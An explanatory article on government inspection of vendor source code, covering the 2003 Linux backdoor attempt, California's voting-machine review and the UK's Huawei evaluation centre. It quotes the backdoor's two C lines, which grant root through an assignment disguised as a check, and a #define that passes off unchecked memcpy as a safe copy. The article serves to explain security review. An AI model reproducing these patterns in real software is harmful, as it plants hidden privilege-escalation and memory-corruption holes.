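# Government-supervised inspection of companies' source code, and what it shows about inspecting AI systems

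## What is source code inspection by a government?

In a government source code inspection, officials, or experts the government appoints or accepts, examine a program's human-readable text, which the vendor normally keeps secret. Governments have sought such inspections for products that public life depends on, such as telephone networks, voting machines, operating systems and antivirus software. They want to know whether a product is safe to rely on, and sometimes whether its maker has hidden anything in it. A similar question now arises for artificial intelligence (AI) systems, whose developers also keep the inner workings private. But much of what matters in these systems is in the weights, the numbers set by training that determine how a model behaves, rather than in the source code.

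### One program, two lines

Programmers write software as source code, text in a programming language that a trained person can read. A program called a compiler translates source code into a binary, the version that a computer can run and that vendors install on equipment. The build is the whole process of producing a binary, including the tools, settings and third-party components used, and "a build" can also mean one result of that process. A binary is a long run of numbers without most of the names and comments that make source code readable, so specialists can recover some of its logic, but slowly.

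An incident from 2003 shows what the readable version can bring to light. Volunteers and companies develop Linux, a free operating system, in the open. On 5 November of that year the developer Larry McVoy noticed a change to the code that lacked the usual record of approval. Someone had apparently broken into a server, according to Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, an account from the university's technology policy centre, and had added two lines to a function that programs call when they need to wait for something to happen:

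```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines look like a routine error check that returns an error code if a program calls the function with a forbidden combination of options. But one character is missing, because the code has `=` where a check would have `==`. In C, `==` tests whether two values are equal, while `=` changes the first value to match the second. `current->uid` holds the ID number of the user running the program, and 0 is the ID of "root", the administrator, who may do anything on the machine.

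If an ordinary program calls the function with exactly those options, the first half of the condition is true and the computer moves on to the second half. That half should check whether the user is root, but it makes the user root instead. In C, an assignment also yields the value assigned, here 0, which counts as false. The whole condition is therefore false, so the second line never runs and no error appears. The program continues with full control of the computer. With any other combination of options, the first half is false and the second half never runs, so nothing unusual happens.

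A tester who had only the finished product would have to try that one combination, which the documentation forbids, and then think to check whether the program's privileges had changed. The source code shows the whole trick on one line, but a reader can still miss it. *Re: BK2CVS problem* (Ladd, 2003) quotes the developers' emails from that day, in which Chad Kitching pointed out that the line set the user's number to zero. McVoy, who had found the unapproved change, replied, "Good eyes, I missed that."

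### Which copy, and which version

The Linux team kept its master copy of the source code in one system and a duplicate in another, for developers who disliked the first system. Only the duplicate contained the two lines, so a reviewer who read the master copy would not have found the flaw that anyone building from the duplicate would have installed. Inspectors of a commercial product face the same difficulty whenever a vendor hands over source code, because the binary on the equipment may have been built from different source code.

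A reproducible build is the cleanest way to show that a binary came from the source code inspectors read. Reproducible Builds' *Definitions* calls a build reproducible if any party with the same source code, build environment and instructions can recreate bit-by-bit identical copies of the result. The environment includes details such as the versions of third-party components and the compiler's settings. Engineers usually compare two binaries by calculating a hash of each, a short fingerprint that changes if the file changes at all. If a product's build isn't reproducible, inspectors can aim for binary equivalence, which means showing that the source code they read produces the binary in use and explaining every remaining difference.

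Even if the inspected source code exactly matches the software in use, the match lasts only until the next update, which installs a new build made from changed source code. When the Russian antivirus company Kaspersky offered its code for review in 2017, the security researcher Chris Wysopal cautioned in the Associated Press' *Kaspersky Lab to open anti-virus software to outside* (2017) that such analyses show only how software works at one moment. Antivirus programs change often, so analyses of them soon become outdated.

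### Vulnerability or backdoor?

A vulnerability is a flaw that an attacker could exploit, whether or not anyone intended it. A backdoor is a hidden means of access or control that someone put in on purpose. The Linux lines could be read as either. In the comments on the Princeton CITP account, several programmers noted that typing `=` for `==` is a common mistake in C, and one suggested that a tired developer with trusted access might have skipped the approval process. Others replied that the check made no sense as honest code, since there was no reason to refuse those options to the administrator alone. The account itself treats the change as a definite attempt at a backdoor, though it says that nobody knows, or will probably ever know, who made it.

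Nearly all the persuasive evidence of intent came from outside the two lines of code, mainly from the apparent break-in and the missing approval. If the same lines had arrived through the normal process under a known programmer's name, they would have had the same effect, but many readers would have blamed carelessness. An inspector who has only the source code can identify a flaw and what an attacker could do with it, but will find it much harder to establish why the flaw is there. A competent saboteur would make a backdoor look like a mistake.

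The distinction also matters less to a government worried about a foreign state, because that state could exploit a vulnerability whether or not anyone planted it. The British case concerns Huawei, a Chinese maker of telecoms equipment, and BT, the company responsible for large parts of the UK's network. *Foreign involvement in the Critical National Infrastructure* (2013), a report by the UK parliament's Intelligence and Security Committee, says that in early 2008 the Security Service advised that the Chinese state might in theory exploit any vulnerabilities in Huawei's equipment to gain some access to BT's network.

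### What an inspection can deliver

A government that inspects source code hopes to gain assurance, which is justified confidence, based on evidence, that a product's risks are understood and managed. Assurance comes in degrees, and the size of modern software limits how much of it reading the code can provide. In *Source Code Review of the Sequoia Voting System*, Blaze, Cordero and colleagues (2007) examined a voting system with more than 800,000 lines of code for California. They estimated that a trained engineer can inspect about 100 lines an hour in the best conditions. At that rate, reading the code once would take about 8,000 hours, or roughly four years' work for one person. The eight reviewers had the code for about six weeks.

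Blaze and colleagues chose to inspect the parts most likely to matter for security, as inspectors of large systems generally have to. They wrote that a manual review that found half of all the problems would be doing very well by industry standards, and that their own method was particularly unlikely to discover a disguised backdoor. Finding a serious flaw therefore shows that the product has one, but a clean report is much weaker evidence that it has none. How much weaker depends on what the inspectors read, how long they had and who picked the sample.

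### Why governments ask

Governments ask to inspect a product when they depend on it but did not make it and cannot easily replace it. In 2003 BT began a £10 billion upgrade of its network and told officials that Huawei wanted part of the work. BT signed a contract with Huawei in 2005 and began installing the equipment across the network in January 2007. The Intelligence and Security Committee found that officials knew the government had powers to intervene but judged the likely trade, financial and diplomatic consequences too significant, and that they did not inform ministers until 2006. The Joint Intelligence Committee, which prepares assessments for the government, had meanwhile warned that an attack through such equipment "would be very difficult to detect or prevent". Inspection offered a middle course between removing the equipment, which was expensive, and trusting it unchecked, which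 was uncomfortable.

California had a similar problem and a fixed deadline. The state and its counties had spent or set aside about $450 million to upgrade voting equipment, according to the California Secretary of State's *Frequently Asked Questions About Secretary of State Debra Bowen’s Top-To-Bottom Review* (2007). A replacement system could be ready for the 2008 elections only if it had federal certification and its maker had submitted it to the state by 1 July 2007. Officials had to find out what they could about the machines they already owned.

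Vendors have their own reasons to agree to inspection. It can keep open a market that a government might otherwise close to them, and it reassures customers who want to check the code themselves.

### Three arrangements

California made inspection a condition of selling voting systems in the state. State law and the certification agreements that many vendors had signed let the Secretary of State, who is in charge of elections, review the systems at any time and charge vendors for the cost. In 2007 Secretary of State Debra Bowen used those powers for a "top-to-bottom review" directed by University of California computer scientists. Some teams read source code and documents, while red teams tried to break into the machines as an attacker would and passed leads to the teams doing the reading. If a vendor declined to take part, Bowen could begin to decertify its system.

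The British government chose a permanent centre that the vendor, Huawei, owned and paid for. The Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) opened in Banbury in November 2010 under arrangements between Huawei and the government. Its staff had to hold the same security clearance as members of the intelligence services. From 2014 an Oversight Board supervised it. The head of the National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), part of the intelligence agency GCHQ, chaired the board, and a senior Huawei executive was deputy chair (HCSEC Oversight Board, *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2019*, 2019).

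Microsoft and Kaspersky run their own reading rooms, which they call transparency centres. Microsoft's programme has members from over 40 countries and international organisations, according to its *Government Security Program*, and offers them four centres and a website where they can read, but not alter, selected source code. Kaspersky lists thirteen centres, where visitors can also compile the software from source and compare the result with the public version. Kaspersky may refuse requests that could cause a security breach, and it bars intelligence and law enforcement agencies that have a mandate or capability for offensive cyber operations. The exclusion addresses a real risk, since people who find flaws by reading source code can also exploit them.

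### Chronology

- January 2003: Microsoft (2003) announced its Government Security Program, which gave national governments controlled access to Windows source code. NATO and a Russian body, Atlas, had already signed.
- 2003: BT told UK officials of Huawei's interest in its network upgrade.
- 2005: BT signed its contract with Huawei.
- 2006: Officials informed ministers, when they needed approval for checks on Huawei's equipment.
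- May to August 2007: California carried out its review, and on 3 August Bowen announced new security requirements and conditions of use, as the California Secretary of State records.
- November 2010: HCSEC opened.
- June 2013: The Intelligence and Security Committee published its report on Huawei and BT.
- December 2013: The UK National Security Adviser's *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre* (2013) responded to the committee's doubts about the centre's independence.
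- Early 2014: The government set up the Oversight Board.
- October 2017: Kaspersky announced its transparency initiative, amid allegations, which Fortune (2017) reported, about how Russian spies had learned of tools that its antivirus software was able to detect.
- November 2018: Kaspersky opened its first centre, in Zurich, according to Kaspersky's *Global Transparency Initiative*.
- 2020: The UK government changed its policy on Huawei. The Oversight Board had no input into the decisions, according to the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2020* (2020).
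- 2021: The HCSEC Oversight Board issued its seventh annual report.
- July 2023: Kaspersky extended source code review to all the products that customers run on their own machines.
- 2026: Kaspersky was still running its centres, and published reports on government requests for data and technical expertise in the first half of the year.

### Six points of comparison

"The government inspected the code" can describe any of these arrangements, but they provide different levels of assurance. A vendor can usually withdraw access it has granted. Inspectors may be more lenient with their own employer. Nobody reads all the code, so whoever picks the sample strongly influences what is found. If the findings stay private, there is little pressure on anyone to fix the product. The table lists the formal terms of each arrangement.

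| | California's review, 2007 | HCSEC, from 2010 | Microsoft and Kaspersky |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who can compel access? | The Secretary of State | Huawei agreed to give access; a 1984 Act held a power in reserve | Nobody, under the programmes' own terms |
| Who employs the inspectors? | The University of California engaged them, under contract to the state | Huawei, with government security vetting | The visiting government or customer |
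| What do they see? | Source code, documents and working machines | Source code, and equipment set up like the operators' networks | Source code that the vendor offers; at Kaspersky also updates and detection rules |
| Who chooses what they examine? | The Secretary of State chose the systems, the reviewers the code | Telecoms operators, the NCSC and HCSEC together; the NCSC signs off the plan | The visitor, within the vendor's offer |
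| Who publishes? | The Secretary of State, without the trade secrets | The Oversight Board, once a year | Neither vendor's description provides for public findings |
| What follows from a bad result? | The Secretary of State can withdraw approval or set conditions | Operators manage the risk; the Board advises the National Security Adviser | Nothing automatic; a government can stop buying |

In California, one official could demand the code and take the product out of use. The British government's position was weaker. The Telecommunications Act 1984 allowed it to require access to source code and to restrict operators to approved products, but its lawyers expected a court challenge if it used those powers, and it would have had to compensate the operator for losses. A government that inspects code in a reading room can only refuse to buy the product, like any other customer, which gives it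 little leverage if there is no alternative.

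## Who controlled the Huawei evaluation centre?

Huawei owned and funded HCSEC and employed its staff, while the British government vetted them, approved their work programme and chaired the board that supervised them. A parliamentary committee examined the arrangement in 2013 and wanted the inspectors moved onto the government's payroll, but the government declined and strengthened the supervision instead. Huawei therefore kept control of the budget and the supply of code and equipment, and kept the power to issue the letter authorising HCSEC's managing director to run the centre.

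### From BT's contract to Banbury

BT told officials about Huawei's interest in its network upgrade at a working group where companies and the government exchanged security information. There was no formal procedure for assessing the risk. The Cabinet Office first told the Intelligence and Security Committee that officials had thought they could not block the contract. It later acknowledged that they had known they could block it but had decided not to, partly because BT might have claimed hundreds of millions of pounds in compensation. In 2004 the government's Intelligence and Security Co-ordinator offered BT technical help but left the decision to the company. In March 2005 a government body that advised on protecting infrastructure recommended that operators not use equipment from untrusted suppliers. BT awarded Huawei the contract that December.

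Officials had a chance to warn a minister before then. Patricia Hewitt, the trade and industry secretary, discussed the contract with BT because of its effect on competition, but officials did not raise the security concerns with her. The Home Secretary was the first minister to hear of them, in January 2006, when the Co-ordinator asked for agreement to help BT monitor Huawei's work. The UK government accepted in its *Government Response to the Intelligence and Security Committee's Report of Session 2013-14* (2013) that officials should have told ministers earlier.

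For the next four years, BT and GCHQ managed the risk together. BT set up security teams to work with GCHQ on the equipment and the contract terms, and GCHQ's experts helped BT design the network to make attacks difficult. These measures protected only BT, and Huawei was winning contracts with other operators. The UK Government gave this as the reason HCSEC opened only in 2010, saying the centre would give the other operators the protection BT already had. Officials took their concerns to Huawei's British subsidiary in February of that year and proposed the centre, which opened in November.

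HCSEC's main job at first was to assess updates before operators installed them, because GCHQ's experts believed an attacker would most likely hide malicious code in an update. Staff would also sample new products at random. The Cabinet Office told the Intelligence and Security Committee that the aim was to reduce the risk of using Huawei's equipment to about that of using equipment from established manufacturers, including large American ones. HCSEC could therefore meet its aim and still leave a good deal of risk in the network.

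### What the committee found in 2013

HCSEC had 22 staff in January 2013, all of them UK nationals on Huawei's payroll. They were a mixture of former officials, industry experts and recent graduates. Operators could choose whether to use the centre, and only three of the five with Huawei equipment did. The other two were major broadband providers. The government said it encouraged operators to use HCSEC only if they served the government or critical infrastructure, or were large enough for a failure to have a significant impact. The Intelligence and Security Committee doubted that two major broadband providers fell outside these criteria.

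More seriously, HCSEC went more than a year without some of the code it needed. Telecoms equipment runs product code, written for one type of device, on top of platform code that provides more general functions. HCSEC needed both, but Huawei's headquarters was reluctant to let all of it leave China. Huawei accepted a solution proposed by HCSEC, and staff downloaded the first platform code in March 2012, sixteen months after the centre opened and more than six years after BT awarded the contract. GCHQ called the delay a "major issue", but added that BT's own contract terms had provided extra assurance since 2005.

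The committee had assumed that GCHQ ran HCSEC with Huawei's money. When it learned that Huawei both funded and ran the centre, it concluded that a "self-policing arrangement" was highly unlikely to provide, or be seen to provide, the necessary assurance. It strongly recommended that the staff become GCHQ employees. If that proved impossible, it wanted GCHQ, at the very least, to audit the centre's work and the government to help select the staff. It also asked the National Security Adviser to review the centre's effectiveness urgently.

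### The dispute over who should employ the inspectors

GCHQ told the committee it had guarded against undue influence. HCSEC's director had spent 40 years at GCHQ and was the only non-Chinese employee at Huawei with full power over budgets and hiring. The technical staff answered to him, and GCHQ said no Chinese national had a say in their pay, bonuses or promotion.

GCHQ also argued that employing the centre's staff through Huawei had advantages. Staff could use Huawei's defect tracking system, an internal database of known flaws and progress in fixing them, which companies almost never open to outsiders. They could also press Huawei's engineers in China to write better code. In GCHQ's experience, independent testers such as the firm EWA Canada had too little influence inside a large company to do that.

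The Intelligence and Security Committee was not persuaded. It reasoned that if companies "almost never" gave outsiders access to defect databases, they must sometimes do so, and that Huawei's commercial reasons for withholding such data from other companies did not apply to GCHQ. It also objected that GCHQ had compared Huawei's employees with outside contractors, when the committee had proposed using GCHQ's own staff. Finally, it argued that better engineering would remove accidental flaws but would not protect the UK against planted ones.

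Kim Darroch, the UK National Security Adviser, sided with GCHQ in December 2013. His review accepted that Huawei's employment of the centre's staff appeared to create conflicts of interest, but judged it the best way to keep complete access to products, code and engineers. He also argued that Huawei's nondisclosure agreements with hundreds of component suppliers would complicate access for anyone outside the company, and that taxpayers might become liable for commercial losses if GCHQ placed itself between Huawei and the British market. Darroch described Huawei's co-operation as exemplary after some early problems. He recommended an Oversight Board, an annual audit and a leading role for GCHQ in senior appointments, measures close to the committee's fallback position.

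### How the arguments held up

The argument from access did not hold up well, because being Huawei employees did not by itself get the inspectors complete code. HCSEC's staff were already Huawei employees during the sixteen months when they had no platform code. The *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board Annual Report 2018* (2018) describes a similar problem that came to light later. Huawei's headquarters had been extracting only a subset of the source code from its repositories to send to Banbury. The Oversight Board insisted on complete code and agreed a timetable for Huawei to redeliver it for every product by December 2017. Huawei finished three months early, and HCSEC observed that all the new packages contained more code than the old ones.

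There is also little sign that employees could reform the company from within, though outside inspectors might have done no better. During 2014 HCSEC sent Huawei's developers in China more than 100 reports on security measurements and worrying practices, and the government thought the effort was starting to work. But in March 2019 the HCSEC Oversight Board reported no material progress on the engineering problems it had described a year earlier. It noted that Huawei had made strongly worded commitments since 2012 without any discernible improvement.

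The nondisclosure agreements were a real obstacle, because Huawei's promises to its suppliers would have bound it even if the inspectors had worked for GCHQ. The suppliers might have consented to government inspection, but asking hundreds of them would have taken time. This was never tested, because the inspectors stayed within the Huawei group throughout.

The evidence supports the committee's fear of self-policing no better than it supports GCHQ's case. HCSEC reported several hundred vulnerabilities and other issues to British operators in 2018 alone. From that year the Oversight Board, whose members included Huawei executives, unanimously agreed reports that offered only "limited assurance" about the company's equipment. Huawei is unlikely to have wanted these findings published, which suggests that it either could not suppress them or chose not to. Inspectors could still have been lenient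 in ways that a published report would not show, for example by looking less hard at an awkward component. But the government found no reason to suspect this, and the NCSC repeatedly praised the quality of the inspectors' work.

### The Oversight Board

The Board met about four times a year to check HCSEC's independence and competence. It advised the National Security Adviser, who in turn reassured ministers and parliament. Its first membership list, in *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) Oversight Board 1st Annual Report 2015* (2015), had eleven names: six officials, two people from BT and Vodafone, and three Huawei employees, including HCSEC's managing director. By the Board's 2021 report, there were five officials and four members from Huawei, so the government no longer had a majority by itself.

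The Board's rules mattered more than its membership numbers. The Board worked by consensus, but GCHQ, as chair, could make the final decision if members disagreed. The National Security Adviser appointed the chair, who invited the other members. Operators' representatives sat as individual experts and had to withdraw if their company had a commercial interest in the discussion. Huawei could, however, veto changes to the terms of reference, because every member had to confirm an amendment in writing.

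The HCSEC Oversight Board stayed out of HCSEC's daily operations and the commercial dealings between Huawei and the operators. In 2019 it stressed that it had no remit to direct or influence what operators bought. It could warn that a product was risky, but the operators decided whether to install it.

### Vetting and appointments

Every inspector needed a security clearance called Developed Vetting, which typically took six months. In the meantime, new recruits worked under escort, and cleared colleagues reviewed everything they did. Some people resigned when they saw the security questionnaire. Three recruits failed vetting after starting work in 2017 and another in 2018, and HCSEC removed all four. Vetting also slowed recruitment, because HCSEC needed UK nationals with rare skills who could pass and were willing to work in Banbury. HCSEC had 25 staff in 2014 and 39 at the end of 2020.

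Vetting is designed to catch people with hidden loyalties or weaknesses that a hostile state could exploit. It offers little protection against pressure from an employer through pay, and GCHQ's assurances to parliament on this point proved too generous. The auditors who examined HCSEC in 2014 found that the senior management board of Huawei's British subsidiary had been calculating the inspectors' bonuses by company criteria. HCSEC's managers learned the amounts only after Huawei had issued them. The HCSEC Oversight Board rated the risk as low and arranged for HCSEC's managers to review future allocations, but Huawei still set the terms of employment.

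GCHQ also could not make senior appointments alone. It was to "lead and direct" the choice of managing director, technical director and solutions and programme director, but a memorandum between GCHQ and Huawei required a unanimous decision, so each could block the other's candidate. When David Pollington was appointed managing director, Huawei drafted the job description and GCHQ agreed it. A recruitment firm found candidates, and the two sides chose three to interview. Two senior GCHQ officials and Huawei's global cyber security officer interviewed them at GCHQ's London office. Pollington, who had spent twelve years at Microsoft, then travelled to Huawei's headquarters in Shenzhen in January 2015 for the company to ratify his appointment. The government thought the process had taken too long and was too complex.

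### Work programme, deliveries and reports

The NCSC, HCSEC and the operators set priorities together each year, partly to stop any one operator from dominating the programme for commercial reasons. One of the NCSC's two technical directors then approved the plan, and the NCSC and the operators concerned had to agree to any later changes. The NCSC wanted HCSEC to evaluate every relevant product at least once every two years, and in 2018 HCSEC was meeting that target on average. Huawei could ask the centre to do work for customers abroad, but only with the British government's agreement.

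HCSEC could evaluate only what Huawei sent it, so its Oversight Board formalised delivery deadlines of 12 weeks for hardware and 30 days for source code. The Board reported that in 2019 Huawei fulfilled five of 30 hardware requests and three of 27 software requests late. One of the late software deliveries held up a scheduled review until the managing director intervened. Auditors had raised the same problem in each of the two previous years and recommended that HCSEC put a "required by" date on each request and escalate any breach. There was no published penalty for lateness.

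The timing of reports also mattered. Huawei could prepare its response or try to soften the findings if it saw a report before the government did, but telling it much later would leave the flaw open for longer. Since 2012 HCSEC had sent its results to the NCSC, the affected operators and Huawei's headquarters at the same time. This meant that details of unrepaired flaws in British networks went straight to China, so the rules allowed HCSEC to delay telling Huawei about a flaw of national significance while the British side assessed it and reduced the danger. The HCSEC Oversight Board recorded that this happened in 2019.

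The auditors for that year also found that Huawei had received three reports before their formal release to the NCSC or the operators. All three concerned issues HCSEC had rated low impact. HCSEC changed its software so that staff could generate a report for Huawei only after one existed for the British side.

### The independence audit

The accounting firm Ernst & Young audited HCSEC's independence every year from 2014, checking whether its staff could work free of undue influence from the rest of Huawei, as the 2010 arrangements required. The government paid for the audit. GCHQ had invited three firms to consider the work, and the Board's chair and deputy chair had to approve the auditor, so Huawei had a say in the choice. Auditors with security clearance examined budgeting, personnel, procurement, planning, co-operation from the rest of Huawei and the release of reports.

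In each audit, the auditors settled the scope, ran a preliminary review and then carried out the full audit. In the first year, the preliminary review was partly meant to let HCSEC deal with any problems before the final report. That is sensible if the aim is to improve controls, but it makes a clean result less impressive than one from a surprise inspection. Year after year, the Board concluded that the arrangements for independence were working "robustly and effectively".

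Much of what a sceptic would want to know lay outside the audit. The HCSEC Oversight Board listed three main exclusions:

- The auditors gave no opinion on whether the overall governance model was appropriate. This was the heart of the parliamentary committee's objection, so even a perfect audit could not answer it. They also took as given the annual budget that Huawei had agreed with HCSEC.
- They did not assess the skill of the inspectors or the quality of their tests. The NCSC reviewed these separately each year.
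- They did not examine physical access to the building or access to its computers. An intruder in those systems could have read HCSEC's findings early, and the audit would not have revealed it. Government security teams did assess HCSEC's new premises, which it occupied in 2018, and judged them sufficiently secure.

### The strains of 2020

HCSEC's independence formally depended on a letter that only Huawei could issue, which gave the managing director authority over money, hiring and purchasing. The letter in force during 2020 expired on 20 December, and the auditors found that Huawei had not replaced it. Huawei had issued a new one by June 2021, when the HCSEC Oversight Board published its report on the year. The Board was satisfied that the lapse had not affected HCSEC's independence.

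Huawei's deliveries also got worse, and it missed the deadline for six of nine hardware requests in 2020. The pandemic may explain some of the delays. It badly disrupted the centre, because inspectors could do their core work only inside the secure building, and product evaluations fell from 42 in 2019 to 24. The Board accepted the delays because they had not reduced HCSEC's effectiveness, but noted that the auditors had made similar findings in previous years and that the problem remained unresolved.

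The NCSC was supposed to decide, at its sole discretion, which products HCSEC analysed, but what the HCSEC Oversight Board called "a contractual matter" limited its choice in practice, at least for a time. The matter arose from uncertainty about a telecommunications security bill, then before Parliament, that would change how the government managed risky vendors. The Board did not describe the contract or name the products. It insisted that no contract or negotiation should unduly constrain the NCSC, and added only that Huawei understood its position.

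American sanctions revealed a disadvantage of Huawei's ownership of HCSEC that had played no part in the 2013 argument. In May 2019 the United States put Huawei on its Entity List, which restricts a company's access to American technology, and it later added Huawei's British subsidiary. HCSEC was part of that subsidiary, so the restrictions also applied to the inspectors. The HCSEC Oversight Board reported that the restrictions had impeded or delayed the purchase of some testing tools and equipment, a problem GCHQ employees would probably not have had.

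The United States tightened the sanctions during 2020, and Huawei and the NCSC agreed that moving HCSEC out of the British subsidiary was the only way to keep it running. On 1 November 2020 they transferred it to a new company, Cyber Security Evaluations Limited, which existed only to hold the centre and was not on the Entity List. Ernst & Young continued to audit the same controls, and Huawei Technologies in China remained the indirect parent.

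## What did inspectors find in Huawei's code, and was it fixed?

HCSEC found serious flaws in Huawei's products year after year, many of them elementary. Huawei generally repaired the flaws it learned of, though sometimes slowly, and one repair introduced a new weakness. But the inspectors saw no comparable change in how the company wrote software, so they kept finding new flaws.

### How HCSEC examined a product

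During 2015 HCSEC divided its work into two kinds of evaluation, according to the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2016* (2016). In one kind, the product evaluation, staff tested a single piece of equipment by itself, without knowing how an operator meant to use it. They used automated tools to test how it handled unexpected messages, check the security settings Huawei had declared and scan some of the source code. HCSEC used this fairly mechanical method mainly for updates to products it had already evaluated, and for low-risk equipment that an attacker could not easily reach.

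In a solution evaluation, the inspectors recreated part of an operator's network in the laboratory, using the operator's real settings where possible, and examined it as an attacker would. They began with a list of areas to investigate, based on how the operator used the equipment, which flaws HCSEC had already reported and whether Huawei claimed to have fixed them. They revised the list as they learned more. These evaluations took so much work that HCSEC aimed for only four a year.

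| Year | Product evaluations completed | Solution evaluations completed |
|---|---|---|
| 2015 | 10 | 4 |
| 2017 | 27 | 3 |
| 2018 | 39 | 3 |
| 2019 | 42 | 4 |
| 2020 | 24 | 5 |

HCSEC had about 30 staff when it published the 2015 figures and 38 at the end of 2018, according to the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2019* (2019). Output grew much faster than staff because HCSEC automated more of the work. The NCSC thought the analysts could not have examined Huawei's equipment effectively without tools that scanned all of it. Nearly all the growth was in product evaluations, so HCSEC covered more equipment but did not do many more of its deepest examinations. The pandemic caused the fall in 2020.

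HCSEC and GCHQ ranked types of equipment by how widely operators used them, how sensitive the data was and how easily an attacker could reach them. Mobile base stations and related radio equipment ranked as a high priority. The ranking used no information specific to Huawei and could have applied to any manufacturer.

Operators did not have to follow HCSEC's evaluations. One operator went ahead with a Huawei text-messaging system despite problems with its evaluation, expecting to upgrade to a later version that HCSEC would evaluate. When the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2018* (2018) came out, the operator had still not upgraded to a version HCSEC could evaluate.

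### A different program for each operator

The NCSC expected Huawei to supply the same version of a product to every British operator and to sell that version widely abroad. A single evaluation would then have served all the operators, and HCSEC could have drawn on other countries' findings. But Huawei supplied different code to different operators, and in 2019 HCSEC had to analyse five versions of its 5G base station for four operators. Huawei said the versions belonged to one global product line, but the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2020* (2020) records that the NCSC had no evidence of this and that the modifications to the common code were extremely large.

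By 2015, HCSEC had found that a small change in a version number did not always mean a small change in the code, so version numbers were little help in deciding what to re-examine. Huawei also tested some builds with the settings a particular operator planned to use. This made the equipment more reliable with those settings, but the HCSEC Oversight Board warned that it could hide serious faults that would appear if the settings changed.

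Repairs had the same problem as evaluations, because HCSEC could not assume that a flaw Huawei had fixed in one operator's version was also fixed in the others. In 2018, newer versions still contained some serious vulnerabilities that HCSEC had reported in earlier evaluations.

### What kinds of flaw?

Many of the vulnerabilities were serious and basic. Some programs that handled messages from the public could write more data into part of their memory than would fit, which can let an attacker take control. Other programs failed when they received malformed messages. Inspectors also found weak cryptography, faulty logic and default passwords. Huawei could have found some of the issues itself with widely available scanning tools. The HCSEC Oversight Board noted that such tools found them when HCSEC tried out its product evaluations in 2015.

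An attacker who knew of these vulnerabilities and could reach the equipment might have been able to read users' traffic, change the equipment's settings or disable part of a network. Most operators had designed their networks to make it hard to reach, which reduced the risk. The NCSC said in 2020 that, to the best of its knowledge, nobody had exploited this set of vulnerabilities in the UK.

HCSEC counted several hundred vulnerabilities and issues for 2018. The Oversight Board said that many of the vulnerabilities were high-impact, described the main types, and judged the total broadly in line with earlier years after allowing for the extra evaluations. *The 2019 Huawei cyber security evaluation report*, a critical post on the blog Shape of Code, called the total meaningless because it could cover one minor vulnerability and several hundred spelling mistakes. That goes too far, given what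 the Board said about the vulnerabilities' impact and types.

But Shape of Code was right that the Board gave no breakdown by severity and no comparison with other manufacturers. The missing comparison is the more serious gap, because without it nobody could tell from the Board's reports whether HCSEC had met its original aim of making Huawei's equipment about as safe to use as established manufacturers' equipment. The Board measured Huawei against "industry good practice", which Huawei's competitors may not have met either.

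### Two versions of a 4G base station

The most detailed published test of Huawei's progress came in 2018. That June, the Oversight Board asked HCSEC to compare two major versions of Huawei's 4G base station software. Huawei had planned to have its improved development methods generally in place by about the time it finished the later version, so that version should have been clearly better.

The code improved in some respects. OpenSSL is a free code library that many products use to encrypt communications. When its developers correct a flaw, a manufacturer has to update every copy in its products, which is easier when there are fewer copies. The earlier base station software had 70 full copies, from four versions of OpenSSL, and 304 partial copies, from 14 versions. The later software had six full copies and 17 partial ones.

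Huawei had removed more than 90% of the copies of OpenSSL, but fragments of ten OpenSSL versions were still scattered through the software, along with OpenSSL files that Huawei had modified. The HCSEC Oversight Board reported that the later version of the software appeared to contain code with ten publicly known vulnerabilities, some dating back to 2006, which an attacker could have simply looked up.

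The Shanghai visit had already suggested how the copies accumulated. Huawei presented its process for managing outside components, with some evidence that staff followed it. The NCSC then chose OpenSSL as an example. A search of Huawei's live development database showed that the company allowed its products to use an unmanageable number of OpenSSL versions, which a description of the process would not have revealed. Some of these versions were unsupported and had known vulnerabilities.

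HCSEC also examined how the base station software copied data in memory. The older copying functions in the C programming language do not check whether the destination has enough room, so an oversized message can overwrite neighboring data. Safer versions require the programmer to specify the destination's capacity and will not copy more than fits. Huawei had required its programmers to follow a secure coding standard since 2013, and its rules prohibited the unsafe functions. HCSEC counted how often the software called each kind.

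| Task | Calls to safe functions | Calls to unsafe functions | Unsafe share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copying blocks of data | Over 5,000 | Over 600 | About 11% |
| Copying text | Over 1,400 | Over 400 | About 22% |
| Assembling formatted text | Over 2,000 | Almost 200 | About 9% |

These figures cover a single circuit board and exclude indirect calls. The board needed especially careful programming because it processed messages from untrusted sources. An unsafe call is not always exploitable, because the surrounding code may check the size first, but its safety then depends on a programmer having remembered the check.

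Some code that looked safe was not. In C, a line beginning with `#define` tells the compiler to replace one piece of text with another before it translates the program. The inspectors found lines of this form:

```
#define SAFE_LIBRARY_memcpy(dest, destMax, src, count) memcpy(dest, src, count)
```

A programmer who uses the "safe" function on the left supplies the destination, its capacity (`destMax`), the source and the amount to copy. The compiler discards the capacity and substitutes the old `memcpy`, which does no checks. A reviewer who saw only the name `SAFE_LIBRARY_memcpy` elsewhere in the code would reasonably conclude that the program was checking the size.

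Another definition did call a safe function, but passed the amount of data to copy as the destination's capacity. The function compared a number with itself, so the check always passed. HCSEC based its count on the binary, where the compiler had already made the replacements. The count would have exposed the first trick, but calls using the second would still have looked safe.

The HCSEC Oversight Board concluded that some developers "may be actively working to hide bad coding practice rather than fix it". They may have been hiding it from their own managers, since the definitions let a programmer appear to obey Huawei's rules without rewriting any code. HCSEC also found that developers had inappropriately switched off warnings from automated checking tools. The later version was better than the earlier one on several measures but still had a significant number of major defects.

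### The outdated operating system

Many of Huawei's products ran on an old operating system from another company. All the programs on this system shared one area of memory, so an attacker who exploited a flaw in any of them could take over the rest. In September 2017, during a visit to Huawei's headquarters in Shenzhen, the NCSC found that Huawei was not properly controlling some security-critical software from outside suppliers. Existing support for this software would end in 2020, although Huawei had promised to support many of the products for longer.

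Four years earlier, in a 2013 white paper, Huawei had said that a central repository let it manage outside code throughout the code's life, including when the original developer stopped supporting it. But the HCSEC Oversight Board noted that the NCSC, not Huawei, had identified the operating system problem, and that repairs in the networks did not begin until 18 months later.

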